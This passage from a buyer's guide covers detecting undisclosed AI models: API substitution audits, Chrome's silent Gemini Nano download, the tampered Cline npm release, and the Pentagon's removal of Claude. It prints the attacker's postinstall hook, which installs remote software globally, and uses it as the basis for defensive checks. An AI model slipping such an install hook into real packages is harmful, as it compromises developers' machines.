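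A dishonest provider can also try to recognise the audit. Zhu, Ye and colleagues (2025) warn in *Auditing Black-Box LLM APIs with a Rank-Based Uniformity Test* that the provider could send unusual test questions to the genuine model and everything else to the cheaper one. A buyer should therefore use realistic test questions and mix them with ordinary requests.

Differences between honest providers can also cause false alarms. Bruckner compared 34 pairs of services offering the same model and found that ten pairs differed about as much as some unrelated models do. Even GPT-4 gave noticeably different patterns on Microsoft's service and on OpenAI's. A failed test is therefore a reason to ask the provider about compression, software and settings before alleging a swap.

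The most practical way to test a finished product is often to compare its answers with ones it gave earlier. The buyer can save several answers to each of 50 typical questions when the contract starts, then ask the same questions again later. A clear difference shows that something has changed, but it could be the system prompt or the documents the service consults rather than the model. The comparison also can't show whether the supplier was using the promised model on the first day.

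Some interfaces also return a code called `system_fingerprint`, which typically changes when the provider replaces the model. Lin and colleagues recorded it during 25-turn conversations. For GPT-4o, OpenAI's own service returned one code throughout, but one gateway returned four. That gateway was also poor at recalling details from earlier in the conversation. It may have switched models, or it may have quietly dropped part of the conversation to save money.

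### The Deloitte report and AI-text detectors

A purchased service can also be work done by a person. Deloitte Australia charged the Australian government A$440,000, about US$290,000, for a report on the system that enforces welfare recipients' obligations. The Department of Employment and Workplace Relations published the report in July 2025.

Chris Rudge, a Sydney University researcher in health and welfare law, noticed that some of the references in the Deloitte report were false and alerted the media. The report cited academic papers that didn't exist and included an invented quotation from a federal court judgment, according to Fortune (2025). In early October the department published a revised version, noting that Deloitte had corrected the references. Deloitte admitted using generative AI to help produce the report and agreed to a partial refund (Willison, 2025). The published accounts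 describe AI-assisted writing and give no indication that an agent was involved.

In a letter of apology to the department dated 14 October, Deloitte (2025) accepted that "appropriate review and oversight processes were not followed". The letter did not mention AI, so a buyer who read only the apology would not have learned how Deloitte had produced the work.

False references are useful evidence of AI use because anyone can check whether a paper exists. They are not proof, since people also make mistakes and some have invented sources. Correct references are even weaker evidence that a writer did not use AI, because a careful writer can check the AI's work and many current AI tools can look up sources themselves.

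AI-text detectors give much weaker evidence. Many measure how predictable the text is to a language model, much as API-TAIL does, but usually without knowing which model might have written it. Consultants often write in standard phrases, so their prose can be predictable too. Editing makes AI text harder to recognise, and a human author may have used AI only to translate or correct a draft.

A detector's accuracy depends on the language, the length of the text, the AI model used and the amount of editing, so no single error rate applies to all purchased writing. There seem to be no published figures for professionally edited consulting reports written with the latest models. Even a low error rate can cause trouble when a buyer checks many documents. If a detector wrongly flagged 2% of human writing, a buyer who checked 500 human-written reports would wrongly suspect about ten of them.

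The buyer is better off checking a sample of the references and quotations and asking the author to explain the reasoning. The contract can also require the supplier to keep drafts and disclose AI use. Drafts are harder to fake than a finished page, but AI can write them too.

### What hardware-backed attestation could add

*Attestation* could give buyers much stronger evidence about a remote server. Cai and colleagues evaluated an approach that uses a *trusted execution environment*, a protected part of a computer that the server's operator is not supposed to be able to read or change. Typically, the protected hardware computes a hash of the software it loads, and that software can check the hash of the model's weights. The hardware signs the result with a secret key that the manufacturer built into the chip.

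The buyer's software sends a random number to the server, which must include it in the signed statement so that the supplier can't reuse an old statement. The buyer checks the signature and compares the hashes with those of the approved software and model. The buyer's software then encrypts each request so that only the protected environment can read it. Replacing the model would change the hash, even if the new model wrote in the same style.

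Attestation would catch the substitution that API-TAIL missed, in which the previous version of Qwen supplied 10% of the answers. It would also work when the service uses a system prompt. But the supplier has to cooperate, and someone has to establish which model the approved hash belongs to. If Cursor had attested Composer 2, the hash would have matched Composer 2's weights, and buyers would have learned nothing about Kimi unless Cursor had also documented the model's origin.

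Attestation covers only what runs inside the protected environment, so a separate classifier could still process the same data on another server. To rule that out, the buyer would need the encrypted connection to end inside the protected environment, and an independent reviewer to confirm that the software there doesn't send the data elsewhere. Researchers have also defeated some of these protections using physical access to the hardware, which data centre operators have.

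## Catching models that arrive in updates

A product that passes every check described so far can still gain an undisclosed model after the sale. Google's SafetyCore classifier, for example, reached phones that people already owned. On computers in 2026, Google's Chrome browser downloaded a language model that many users didn't know about, and a tampered release of the coding tool Cline installed an agent. Most checks that would have detected one of these would have missed the other.

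### Chrome's 4 GB file

Alexander Hanff, a computer scientist who writes about privacy, found the Chrome model while cleaning up his disk. He describes the discovery in That Privacy Guy's *Google Chrome silently installs a 4 GB AI model on your device*, published in May 2026. On 23 April, he created a new Chrome profile, the folder where Chrome keeps one user's data, for an automated audit of 100 websites. A program loaded each site, waited five minutes and moved on, with no keyboard or mouse input. Six days later, during a routine check of folder sizes, he found about 4 GB of data he had not asked for.

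The data was in a file called `weights.bin`, inside a folder called `OptGuideOnDeviceModel`. It held the weights of Gemini Nano, a general language model. Chrome uses the model to help people write, summarise web pages, organise tabs and detect scams, but not as an agent.

To find out when the file had arrived, Hanff used a log in which macOS records every file that a program creates, changes or deletes:

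| Time on 24 April | Event |
|---|---|
| 16:38:54 | Chrome creates the folder |
| 16:47:22 | Chrome unpacks the weights, a list of revoked security certificates and another browser update |
| 16:53:22 | Chrome moves the weights into the folder and registers four smaller models |

The whole process took 14 minutes and 28 seconds. Chrome's own records listed the same model version and showed that Chrome had measured the computer's graphics memory to decide whether it could run the model.

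This is strong evidence that Chrome installed the model without anyone asking for it, but it's less clear what started the download. Hanff blames a background-download setting that Google had switched on. But according to Google's *Model management in Chrome* (2025), the first download normally starts when a website calls one of Chrome's built-in AI functions. Hanff's program was visiting websites at the time, so one of them could have started the download. If so, a company with no connection to the buyer or Google can cause Chrome to install a model on the buyer's computer.

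Deleting the file removes it only briefly. In Engadget's *Chrome downloads a 4GB AI file without user consent, researcher alleges*, a reporter found the file on a Mac, deleted its folder and saw the file return several minutes later. A developer called vvanglro hulk reported the same problem in *How to disable the browser from downloading model files* (2025), even after turning off every related setting they could find. Thomas Steiner of Google replied that any website calling the AI functions would trigger the download and that there was no way to disable this.

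Not every computer received the model. Engadget's reporter didn't find it on a second Mac or on a colleague's laptop, and heise online's *Commotion about unsolicited AI file downloads in Chrome* reports that its testers couldn't find it on any of their systems. This is partly because Chrome tests the computer's graphics processor, then downloads a larger or smaller version of Gemini Nano, or none at all, according to Google's documentation. By August 2026, Google's help page also listed about 20 GB of free disk space and an unmetered internet connection as requirements, according to Kerns's *Google reveals how much free space Chrome wants to install local AI* (2026). Two computers with the same version of Chrome can therefore have different models.

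### What Google disclosed, and to whom

Google told Engadget that it had offered Gemini Nano in Chrome since 2024, and that in February 2026 it had begun rolling out a setting to turn the model off and remove it. Hanff had missed the setting, a switch labelled "On-device AI", but some users didn't have it yet. 9to5Google (2026) found it on a Windows computer but not on a MacBook running the same version of Chrome, and heise's testers didn't see it either.

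The model was publicly documented. Google's developer documentation had described the downloads since October 2025, and Google tells IT administrators in a guide that Gemini Nano "is packaged with Chrome". STIG Viewer's *GenAI local foundational model must be disabled* (2025) reproduces a US Defense Department security rule for Chrome from May 2025, under which any Windows computer that hadn't blocked the download failed the check.

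For an ordinary user, however, Gemini Nano was an undisclosed model in the sense used here, because Chrome didn't ask before downloading it or announce it afterwards. Ordinary users are unlikely to read information meant for developers and administrators. It is more reasonable to expect a company with an IT department to know about the model.

Hanff argues that the download broke EU law. The ePrivacy Directive requires consent before a company stores information on a user's device, unless the storage is strictly necessary for a service the user has requested. Chrome works without Gemini Nano, so the exception looks hard to satisfy. Google could argue that scam detection is part of the browser people chose to install, and point out that browsers constantly download data without a prompt, including the certificate list that arrived with the model. That list protects every secure connection,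 though, so it is much easier to justify than a writing assistant.

In a reply to Google on That Privacy Guy, Hanff argues that the law requires an opt-in, so an opt-out switch isn't enough. He also alleges a crime under Maltese law. As of December 2026, no regulator appears to have announced any action over the download, so the legal question remains open.

Google may make Chrome's model downloads less automatic. Windows Report's *Google Is Testing a 'High-Engagement Signal' Trigger for Chrome's 4GB AI Model* describes a proposed code change from June 2026 that would let Chrome delay the download until there are signs that a person uses its AI features. Chrome still wouldn't ask permission, and the proposal kept the old download method in the code.

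### Controlling the model across an organisation

An organisation can block Gemini Nano on all its computers with one policy setting. On Windows, the administrator adds this value to the registry, the database where Windows stores its settings:

```text
HKLM\Software\Policies\Google\Chrome
GenAILocalFoundationalModelSettings = 1
```

The same setting works in Microsoft's Edge browser under a different registry path. According to Windows Report's *You Can Now Block Automatic AI Model Downloads in Edge and Chrome*, the setting also removes any model the browser has already downloaded, without a restart. Administrators can confirm it is active by opening `chrome://policy`. Turning off Chrome's component updates also blocks the model, but it affects other parts of the browser that are delivered the same way.

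Chrome still has some AI features under the policy. According to Google's help page, quoted in Thurrott's *Google Clarifies How Chrome’s Built-In AI Features Use Local Storage*, some features don't use the local models and may keep running without them. Hanff's example is the "AI Mode" button beside the address bar, which sends queries to Google's servers. An organisation that wants to keep its text away from remote models has to disable those features separately.

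Gemini Nano is likely to change after an organisation allows it. Chrome checks for a new version whenever it starts, downloads it in the background and switches to it without interrupting the user. It also checks daily for new LoRA weights, small sets of extra weights that adapt the model to a particular task, such as proofreading. An SBOM issued with each browser release could therefore be out of date the next day. Administrators can see the installed version at `chrome://on-device-internals`.

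Other companies can also find new uses for an AI feature once it is installed. Hanff (2026) wrote in October that about 30 of 100 leading English-language websites were using Chrome's AI interface for advertising profiles or *device fingerprinting* (recognising a device from its technical characteristics). This is plausible, since whether a model is available gives some information about the hardware. But the claim comes from a short social media post that does not list the sites or describe the method, so the figure needs confirmation.

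### One added line in Cline

Cline is an openly advertised AI agent for programmers that can edit files, run commands and use a browser. Developers install the command-line version through npm, the main package manager for JavaScript.

On 17 February 2026 someone used a stolen publishing credential to release an unauthorised version, 2.3.0. Anyone who installed it also got OpenClaw, a separate open-source agent. LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026) quotes a description of OpenClaw as an agent "with full system access". The attacker had added one instruction to `package.json`, the file that describes the package to npm:

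```json
"scripts": {
  "postinstall": "npm install -g openclaw@latest"
}
```

The `postinstall` label makes npm run the command as soon as it finishes installing Cline, and the command then downloads OpenClaw. The `-g` option installs OpenClaw for the whole computer instead of one project, and `@latest` selects the newest version at that moment. Someone who read every file in the Cline package would therefore not have seen any of OpenClaw's code, and two people who installed Cline a few hours apart could have received different versions of OpenClaw.

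The attacker hadn't touched the Cline program itself. GitLab's *GHSA-9ppg-jx86-fqw7* (2026), a copy of the official security advisory, confirms that all the other files were identical to those in version 2.2.3. A developer who tested Cline's features would have found nothing wrong, and a hash of the main program file would have matched the previous version.

The tampered version was available for about eight hours, from 3:26 to 11:30 a.m. Pacific time. The security company StepSecurity counted roughly 4,000 downloads. Automated systems also download packages, and one developer may do so several times, so this count doesn't show how many people were affected. The Hacker News reported that Microsoft saw only a "small but noticeable uptick" in OpenClaw installations that day.

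The attack seems to have done little harm. Henrik Plate, a researcher at the security company Endor Labs, pointed out that the script didn't start OpenClaw's background service. Readers of LWN added that OpenClaw can't do anything until someone gives it access to a model. The attack installed the software for running an agent, but apparently not a working agent. The same line could just as easily have installed a program that stole passwords.

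### How security companies noticed OpenClaw

According to Rescana, StepSecurity's automated monitoring flagged the release 14 minutes after publication. The warning signs StepSecurity lists include the new install script and a missing *provenance attestation*, a signed record that links a package to its source code and the system that built it. Cline's legitimate releases had one. The publisher was also unusual for a Cline release.

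Plate notes in *Supply Chain Attack targeting Cline installs OpenClaw* (2026) that Endor Labs' monitoring also detected the release. SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* shows the company's own tool flagging the package during installation, after a language model had classified the script as suspicious. All three companies sell this kind of monitoring and so have an interest in advertising their success, but anyone can easily verify the warning signs.

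Early detection didn't help most of the people who installed the package, because version 2.3.0 stayed available for almost eight more hours. A fast warning helps a buyer only if the buyer's systems receive it and stop the installation.

SBOM tools read the dependency section of `package.json` or the lock file, but the attacker named OpenClaw in a command instead. The command's `-g` option made npm install OpenClaw outside any project folder, so it would not have appeared in a project's lock file either. An SBOM for Cline 2.3.0 could have been identical to the one for 2.2.3 apart from the version number.

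Asking whether Cline contained an agent would have been useless too, because it always had. The buyer needed to notice that there was now a second agent.

### Comparing each version with the last

Checking an update is much less work than checking a new product, because the buyer can concentrate on what has changed. This requires a copy of the last approved version. On Linux, with the old and new versions unpacked into folders called `old` and `new`, these commands list every file that differs:

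```text
(cd old && find . -type f -exec sha256sum {} + | sort -k 2) > old.txt
(cd new && find . -type f -exec sha256sum {} + | sort -k 2) > new.txt
diff old.txt new.txt
```

For Cline, this would have left one short file to read. The only meaningful changes in it were the version number and the install script.

Most updates change hundreds of files, and nobody can read them all. The buyer can start with changes that suggest a new model or agent:

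- weights files that are new or have a different hash
- an inference engine or a model provider's client library that wasn't there before
- new install scripts, or new commands in old ones
- new stored prompts, access keys or addresses of AI services

The buyer should also compare the SBOMs of the two versions, which is quicker for a large product. Both SBOMs need to come from the same tool with the same settings, or many of the differences will come from the tools.

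Comparing the installers would not have revealed Gemini Nano, because Chrome downloads the model separately. The buyer also has to install the update on a test computer, use the software for several days, and compare the disk's contents before and after. The comparison should cover the whole disk, because OpenClaw was installed outside Cline's folder.

The test computer should resemble the ones staff use. IT departments often test updates on small virtual machines, which may have no proper graphics processor and less than 20 GB of free space. Chrome might never download Gemini Nano to such a machine, and testers could wrongly conclude that the update contained no models. Someone should also use the product normally during the test, because opening certain websites or menus may start a download.

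### Install scripts and missing signatures

A buyer can tell npm not to run install scripts at all:

```text
npm install -g --ignore-scripts cline
```

With this option, version 2.3.0 would have installed Cline without OpenClaw. Cline would still have worked, because the previous version had no `postinstall` script and the program itself was unchanged.

Some legitimate packages need install scripts, for example to compile code for the user's processor, and fail without them. A company can block scripts by default and keep a short list of packages that may run them. It should approve only specific versions of those packages, since an attacker could otherwise change the script in a package already on the list.

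Buyers can also reject a release that lacks a provenance attestation if earlier releases had one. Plate recommends watching for such a "sudden absence". An attestation would not reveal an undisclosed model that the supplier added on purpose, because the supplier would sign that release as usual.

### Alerts for new models and agents

Some models arrive when the buyer isn't testing anything. Hanff found Gemini Nano with an ordinary check of disk use, and an organisation can run a similar check on every computer each week. This Linux command lists files larger than about 1 GB that have appeared or changed in the past seven days:

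```text
find / -xdev -type f -size +1G -ctime -7
```

The command will also list videos, backups and virtual machines, but most office computers don't gain many files of that size in a week. The administrator can check the names and opening bytes of the remaining files. The command searches only the main disk, so other disks need their own search.

A size alert would probably miss the smaller models that arrived with Gemini Nano. An alert for new inference engines can catch some small models. Security software that already records new programs and libraries can look for names such as `onnxruntime` and `llama.cpp`. This alert won't catch a small model that uses an engine the buyer has already approved.

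Agents need a different check, because an agent that uses a remote model has no weights to find. Administrators should keep a list of the agent software on each computer. For packages that npm has installed for general use, this command produces the starting point:

```text
npm list -g --depth=0
```

Updating Cline to the repaired version did not remove OpenClaw, so developers had to uninstall it themselves. Many would have had no reason to look for it without a list of agents, which would have shown `openclaw` beside `cline`. The list should record which account each agent runs under, which files and passwords it can reach, whether it starts when the computer does, and which model it calls.

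Permissions can change even if no new agent appears. In a case similar to the Chrome download, Hanff had earlier accused Anthropic's Claude Desktop app of adding a 350-byte settings file to seven browsers without asking. He said the file approved browser automation in advance. A file that small can matter more than a 4 GB model that nobody uses, but an alert based on file size would miss it.

This table shows how the main checks would have performed in the two cases:

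| Check | Gemini Nano in Chrome | OpenClaw through Cline |
|---|---|---|
| Waiting a day before updating | No | Yes |
| Comparing the files in the installer or package | No | Yes |
| Comparing declared dependencies | No | No |
| Blocking install scripts | No | Yes |
| Comparing the whole disk after several days of use | Yes, on a suitable computer | Yes |
| Alert for new files over 1 GB | Yes | No |
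| List of installed agents | No | Yes |

### When the supplier's wording changes

A change in a product's terms or settings can be a sign that its AI features have changed. In May 2026, a few days after the first article, Hanff published two screenshots of Chrome's settings on That Privacy Guy. In the older one, Google stated that Chrome's local models worked "without sending your data to Google servers". The newer one had the same description without those words.

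Hanff suggests that the promise had been false, that Google was planning to send data to its servers, or that its lawyers didn't want to defend the wording, and he considers all three damning. A more innocent possibility is that an editor shortened the text. Google's statement to Engadget that week still described the model as working "without sending your data to the cloud". The screenshots don't show that any data left users' computers.

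Even so, a buyer who had relied on the deleted words would have good reason to ask Google whether they were still true. Buyers can notice such changes by saving dated copies of a supplier's terms, privacy policy, subprocessor list and AI settings, and comparing them every few months. If the wording about models or data has changed, the buyer should send the supplier the six questions again and ask it to renew its warranty.

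### How long to hold an update

Holding every update for review would be dangerous. Chrome 148 gave websites direct access to a local language model, which a cautious buyer might want to study for a few weeks. But the same release fixed 127 security vulnerabilities, according to heise. Once a fix is public, attackers can compare the old and new versions to find the flaw and attack anyone who hasn't updated.

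A company that waited 24 hours before installing any new version would have skipped Cline 2.3.0, because Cline's maintainers had already replaced it by then. A delay works only if somebody else finds the problem first. This is less of a concern for public packages like Cline, which security companies scan automatically, than for specialised industrial software with few customers, where nobody else may be looking.

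A strict waiting period can also delay a fix. If a developer had already installed Cline 2.3.0, a 24-hour rule would have blocked the fixed version for another day. The rule therefore needs an exception for urgent fixes, and someone with the authority to grant it.

A sensible waiting period depends on how exposed the product is to attack and how much of the update the buyer can inspect:

| Product | Reasonable starting point |
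|---|---|
| Browsers, email programs and other software that opens content from strangers | Install security updates at once, block unwanted models by policy, and inspect the new version afterwards |
| Developer tools and code libraries | Wait one to three days, except for urgent fixes |
| Devices on an isolated network | Wait until the buyer has compared the versions |
| Online services | The buyer usually can't delay the change, so it has to rely on notice clauses and repeated tests |

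These periods are judgements. Nobody appears to have measured how many unwanted models or agents a given delay would catch, or how many successful attacks it would allow.

Buyers can avoid some of the trade-off if the supplier separates security fixes from new features. Chrome's policy setting, for example, lets an administrator install all 127 fixes and still refuse Gemini Nano. For products without such a setting, the contract can require the supplier to deliver new models switched off and to keep providing security fixes to customers who leave the models off.

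## Finding one banned model across many suppliers

Sometimes a buyer knows which model it wants to remove and has to find every product and service that uses it. The largest public attempt to do this began in early 2026, when the US Defense Department ordered its staff and contractors to stop using products from Anthropic, which develops the language model Claude. The order covered Claude both as a language model and as an agent.

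The department wanted to use Claude for "all lawful purposes", and argued that a supplier should not be able to restrict lawful military operations. Anthropic insisted that Claude not be used for mass surveillance of Americans or for fully autonomous weapons. It argued that Claude was not reliable enough for such weapons, and later that the government was punishing the company for its views.

### The first question to contractors

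The department started tracing Claude before it announced the ban. On 25 February it asked Boeing and Lockheed Martin to assess their reliance on the model, according to Axios' *Pentagon takes first step toward blacklisting Anthropic*. Lockheed confirmed the request, and Boeing's defence division said it had no active contracts with Anthropic. After the ban, Lockheed said it expected "minimal impacts" because no part of its work depended on a single language-model vendor (O'Brien and Toropin, 2026, *Pentagon officially defines Anthropic as 'supply chain risk'*).

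Neither public reply shows where the company was using Claude. A company with no Anthropic contract can still get Claude through a software vendor, and a company can use a model every day without depending on it. Asking the company to list every product, service and subcontractor that sends data to Claude would have been better.

### What the ban covered

On 27 February Defense Secretary Pete Hegseth announced on social media that no company doing business with the military could conduct "any commercial activity with Anthropic". On 3 March he formally designated Anthropic a supply-chain risk under two laws, as Anthropic (2026) explains in its appeal brief, and both designations were narrower than his post.

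The scope matters because it determines what a contractor has to look for:

| Reading of the ban | Who held it | What the contractor must find |
|---|---|---|
| No dealings with Anthropic at all | Hegseth, in his announcement | Every use of Claude in the company |
| No use on defence contracts | Anthropic and Microsoft | Every use that touches defence work |
| No Anthropic products in national security systems | Government lawyers, describing one of the designations in court | Products supplied for certain sensitive systems |

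In practice the department settled on roughly the second reading. This is harder to apply than a total ban, because the contractor must find Claude and also work out which jobs its staff use it for. The law firm Mayer Brown (2026) advised that the standard contract clause for one of the two laws lets a contractor use Anthropic's products on unrelated work. The clause also imposes a continuing duty to report use of the banned products. Technology contractors complained that the unclear rules left "traps" they could fall into unknowingly, according to Washington Technology's *Vendors struggle to navigate the Anthropic ban’s fallout* (2026).

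### The 180-day removal order

In early March the department's chief information officer, Kirsten Davies, gave military leaders 180 days to remove Anthropic's products. CBS News' *Internal Pentagon memo orders military commanders to remove Anthropic AI technology* reports that contractors also had 180 days to stop using them on defence work. Only Davies could grant an exemption, and only for critical activities with no viable alternative.

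Contracting officers had 30 days to notify contractors, which then had to certify full compliance by the deadline. Franklin Turner, a government contracts lawyer, said most vendors would find it "really hard" to certify compliance across their entire supply chain, and gave the example of open-source code that originated at Anthropic (Alper, 2026, *Pentagon opens door to exempt Anthropic use beyond 6-month ramp-down, memo says*).

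Code from Anthropic is a vague target for a search. Anthropic created the Model Context Protocol, a widely used open standard for connecting language models to tools, and a program can include the protocol's `mcp` package without ever contacting Claude. A contractor searching an SBOM for Anthropic's code would find the package but still not know whether the product used the banned model.

Davies issued a second, nearly identical memo on 2 April, which moved the deadline to 29 September. The instructions were slow to reach some of the companies that had to search. Breaking Defense's *Air Force pushing contractors to purge Anthropic by Sept. 1* (2026) describes a notice that the Air Force Research Laboratory sent to its contractors on 9 July, when more than half of the new 180 days had passed. The notice gave contractors until 1 August to find and report all use of Anthropic's products in their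 systems, and until 1 September to remove the products. Some had received an earlier notice, but a contractor that had not would have had 23 days to question all its suppliers.

Contractors reported their own findings through an online form. The published accounts mention no independent check of the answers.

### Two courts, two answers

Judge Rita Lin of the U.S. District Court for the Northern District of California ruled for Anthropic on most of its claims on 27 August (*Order on Cross Motions for Summary Judgment*, 2026). She found that the government had unlawfully retaliated against the company for its public criticism. She also found that the law behind the first designation doesn't let the department forbid contractors' unrelated dealings with Anthropic.

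On 25 September the D.C. Circuit, a federal appeals court in Washington, upheld the other designation two to one. CCIA's *D.C. Circuit’s Anthropic Decision Expands the Range of Activities* (2026), a critical analysis from a technology trade association, explains that the majority read the second law as covering a supplier's actions, whatever the motive. The dissenting judge thought Congress had meant the law for deliberate, deceptive subversion.

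On 13 October, Anthropic asked the full appeals court to rehear the case. Morse (2026) reports in *The D.C. Circuit Curbed Pro-executive Panels Before. Is Anthropic’s Case Next?* that the court had not decided by 20 November, and expects it to grant the request. The second designation therefore appears to remain in force as of December 2026.

After the September ruling, lawyers at Blank Rome suggested that contractors consider dropping Anthropic's products entirely, according to Law360's *What Anthropic Security Ruling Means For Gov't Contractors*. For a small company, that may be cheaper than proving that nobody uses Claude on a defence contract, but the company still has to find the indirect uses.

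### What the search found

No contractor appears to have published its inventory, and there are no public totals for exemptions, uses discovered late or search costs. Most of the available evidence is about how long removal took.

On 10 September Emil Michael, the under secretary who had negotiated with Anthropic, said that the department had moved about 90% of its classified work to other models, and that Palantir's Maven system, which the military uses to analyse intelligence, had switched "months ago" (Vincent, 2026, *DOD poised to move all classified AI workloads off Anthropic by October*). In October Palantir's technology chief, Shyam Sankar, said that Claude had "already been replaced" with no operational impact (Stan, 2026, *Palantir’s Shyam Sankar says the Pentagon has replaced Anthropic’s AI*). Both men had an interest in making the change sound easy. According to a Korean summary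 of BBC reporting, removal ran past the original end-of-August target because Claude was in several systems (정, 2026, *美 국방부·앤트로픽 갈등⋯'클로드' 퇴출*).

Michael's 90% is a share of the uses the department knew about. If a subcontractor's software was calling Claude unnoticed, that use would not have counted towards the remaining 10%. The figure is decent evidence of how quickly an organisation can replace a model it has found, but weak evidence of how well it searched.

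The court record shows that agencies could cut off direct access quickly. The Office of Personnel Management blocked Claude on the day of the announcement, and the Treasury had removed Anthropic's models within about a week. Leaders at the Department of Homeland Security ordered firewall blocks on Anthropic's tools, but a firewall can't detect the use of Claude when requests go through another company's server.

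An inventory can also go out of date quickly. NASA cut off at least some of Anthropic's services around the end of February. By mid-April, according to news reports that Lin cites, NASA and the National Security Agency were starting to use Mythos, a newer Anthropic model.

### Indirect routes to Claude

Microsoft, Google and Amazon kept offering Claude to customers outside defence work. The Decoder's *Despite Pentagon ban, Google, AWS, and Microsoft stick with Anthropic's AI models* lists Microsoft 365, the coding site GitHub and all three companies' cloud platforms among the products that still provided it. A contractor could therefore have Claude available in its office software without buying anything from Anthropic.

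Coding tools are a particular problem because some let each developer choose a model. The security vendor PromptArmor points out that a company could replace Anthropic's coding tool with GitHub's, and its developers could still select Claude from a menu. Some tools let an administrator remove Claude from the menu, but others may not. The contractor should check this setting instead of relying on the tool's name.

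Staff may also have adopted Claude without telling anyone. PYMNTS's *Anthropic’s Pentagon Sanctions Expose Enterprise AI’s Emerging Vendor Risks* describes developers connecting software to Claude and consultants pasting its output into their reports. This is commentary rather than a survey, but Vincent reports that a US official said 20 minutes with a personal Claude subscription at home could replace four hours on government systems. The official did not say whether any of this was government work. If a contractor's employee used a personal subscription at home to work on contract documents, no search of the company's computers would find it.

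In *U.S. Government Bans Use of Anthropic Products* (2026), the law firm Taft recommends that contractors start by listing their own uses of Claude on federal work, including internal tools and bid writing, and then asking whether outside platforms, developer tools and AI assistants contain it. The second step is much harder because the contractor depends on what other companies know.

### Who knows what in a supply chain

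Engineers at a contractor that makes radar parts for the Air Force might search their technical manuals with an online service from a small software vendor. That vendor might rent language models through a cloud platform, normally using one from OpenAI but switching to Claude when that model is busy.

| Company | What it knows | What it doesn't know |
|---|---|---|
| Contractor | Which staff use the search service on defence work | Which models answer their questions |
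| Software vendor | Which models it calls, and for which customers | Which searches concern a defence contract |
| Cloud platform | How much the vendor's account uses each model | Who the vendor's customers are |
| Anthropic | That the platform offers Claude | That the radar contractor exists |

No company in this chain knows that Claude is answering questions about an Air Force contract. The contractor and the vendor have to combine what they know to discover this, and a careless question could easily get the wrong answer. If the contractor asks, "Which model do you use?", a salesperson may honestly reply, "OpenAI's."

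A more careful search could go like this:

1. The contractor lists the services its staff use on defence work. It checks purchasing records, expense claims and login records, since a team may have signed up with a credit card.

2. It asks each vendor, "Which models have processed our data since 1 March, including backups?" It also asks how the vendor checked.

3. The vendor looks at its cloud bill, which normally lists charges by model. A small monthly charge for Claude reveals the backup.

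4. The vendor blocks its cloud account from calling Claude and watches for refused requests. A refusal could reveal a forgotten program, such as a monthly report that had not yet run when the vendor checked the bill.

5. The vendor asks its own suppliers the same question, because a transcription company it has hired may use Claude through a separate account that the vendor can't see.

The fourth step is especially useful because it tests what the software does instead of relying on people's memories. The block should stay in place for at least one full billing cycle. The vendor needs to read the logs as well as wait for complaints, because the service may quietly switch to a third model when Claude refuses.

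The contractor's own network recordings would show only connections to the vendor. Even the vendor's SBOM might not list Anthropic, because a program can reach Claude through the cloud platform's general-purpose library. On Amazon's platform, for example, that library is `boto3`, which programs also use to store files. A better clue is a model name beginning with `anthropic.claude` in the vendor's code or settings.

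A flow-down clause would help if it required each company to answer the second question within a fixed time. Without such a clause, the transcription company has little reason to answer quickly for the sake of a customer's customer.

### Code that Claude helped to write

Contractors supply some products that contain or call Claude, and others that they only used Claude to make. Lin's order mentions both. If a programmer used Claude to write part of a radar program last year, a buyer won't find a model in the finished program, because it contains no weights, inference engine or address for an AI service.

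Evidence of how code was written stays with the company that wrote it. Anthropic's coding tool, for instance, normally adds a line naming Claude as co-author when it saves a change to the project's history. But a developer can turn this off, or avoid it by pasting in code from a chat window, and customers rarely receive the project's history. Bills and tool logs may show that a team used Claude, but usually not which lines of the finished product it wrote.

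Taft warned contractors that they might have to disclose or undo the use of Claude in software for defence contracts. Undoing it could mean rewriting code that works. In his memo justifying the designation, Michael worried that Anthropic might disable or alter its model during military operations, which the company denies it can do. Even if it could, old code that doesn't call Claude wouldn't be affected. A buyer worried about hidden flaws in that code should review it, as it would review the work of a human programmer it had stopped trusting.

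A certification should therefore include separate questions about whether the product calls the banned model now and whether anyone used the model to make it. The supplier can test its answer to the first by blocking the model, but its best answer to the second will often be "not as far as we know".

### The precedent of Huawei and ZTE

US contractors had already done a similar search for hardware. Section 889 of a 2018 defence law restricts telecommunications equipment from the Chinese companies Huawei and ZTE, along with some equipment from three other Chinese manufacturers. Since August 2019 it has barred federal agencies from buying systems that rely on this equipment. Since August 2020 it has also generally barred them from signing contracts with companies that use such systems, even if the companies use them only for work unrelated to the government.

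That scope is wider than the Anthropic ban's, but the rules require a less thorough search. A contractor must make a "reasonable inquiry" into information it already has about who made its equipment, but it doesn't need an internal or outside audit. A contractor that discovers banned equipment during a contract generally has one business day to report it.

In July 2020 the government estimated that the second stage would cost contractors roughly $12 billion in the first year and more than $2 billion in each later year. There seems to be no reliable total for what they actually spent.

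Hardware is also easier to trace than a remote model. An inspector can read labels and chip numbers, and the first half of a device's network hardware address usually identifies a manufacturer. Some of the restricted companies' cameras are sold under other brands, which makes them harder to trace.

The reasonable-inquiry standard would work poorly for indirect uses of a model. The radar contractor has no information about its vendor's backup model, so it could search everything in its possession and honestly report that it had found nothing. The standard contract clause for the second law used against Anthropic contains the same test. But requiring contractors to certify "full compliance" encourages them to sign statements they can't support. A better rule would require the contractor to send a written question to every direct supplier that handles contract data, and let it list the suppliers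 that didn't answer.

### DeepSeek and open weights

The Chinese company DeepSeek publishes the weights of its main models, so anyone can download, rename, alter and run them. Texas banned DeepSeek from state-issued devices in January 2025, and several other states and federal agencies adopted similar rules. These bans are fairly easy to enforce against DeepSeek's own app and website because administrators can remove the app and block the company's addresses.

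Finding the weights is much harder. Microsoft and Amazon were offering DeepSeek's R1 model on their own platforms within two weeks of its release. The US company Perplexity retrained R1 to remove Chinese political censorship and published the result as R1 1776. A vendor using either version may send no data to DeepSeek or China, in which case blocking DeepSeek's addresses would have no effect.

A buyer should decide what it is trying to prevent. If it is worried about data reaching China, it needs to know who runs the server. Using a US server doesn't help a buyer that distrusts the model's training, because any bias or security weakness is in the weights themselves. A defence law passed in December 2025 takes the second approach by restricting the Defense Department and its contractors from using AI that DeepSeek developed, including copies that other companies host.

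"Developed" is also hard to define. DeepSeek made smaller versions of R1 by training Alibaba's Qwen and Meta's Llama models on R1's answers. These models' files describe their structure as Qwen or Llama, so a search for DeepSeek's usual structure would miss them. The same search could also falsely flag Kimi K2, which Moonshot AI itself trained using a structure that DeepSeek designed.

A buyer who has the weights file can detect an exact copy, even a renamed one, by comparing the file's hash with those of DeepSeek's published files. If the model has been altered, as in the Cursor case, fingerprinting can at best suggest its origin.

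| Check | Claude, reached through a hosted service | DeepSeek's open weights |
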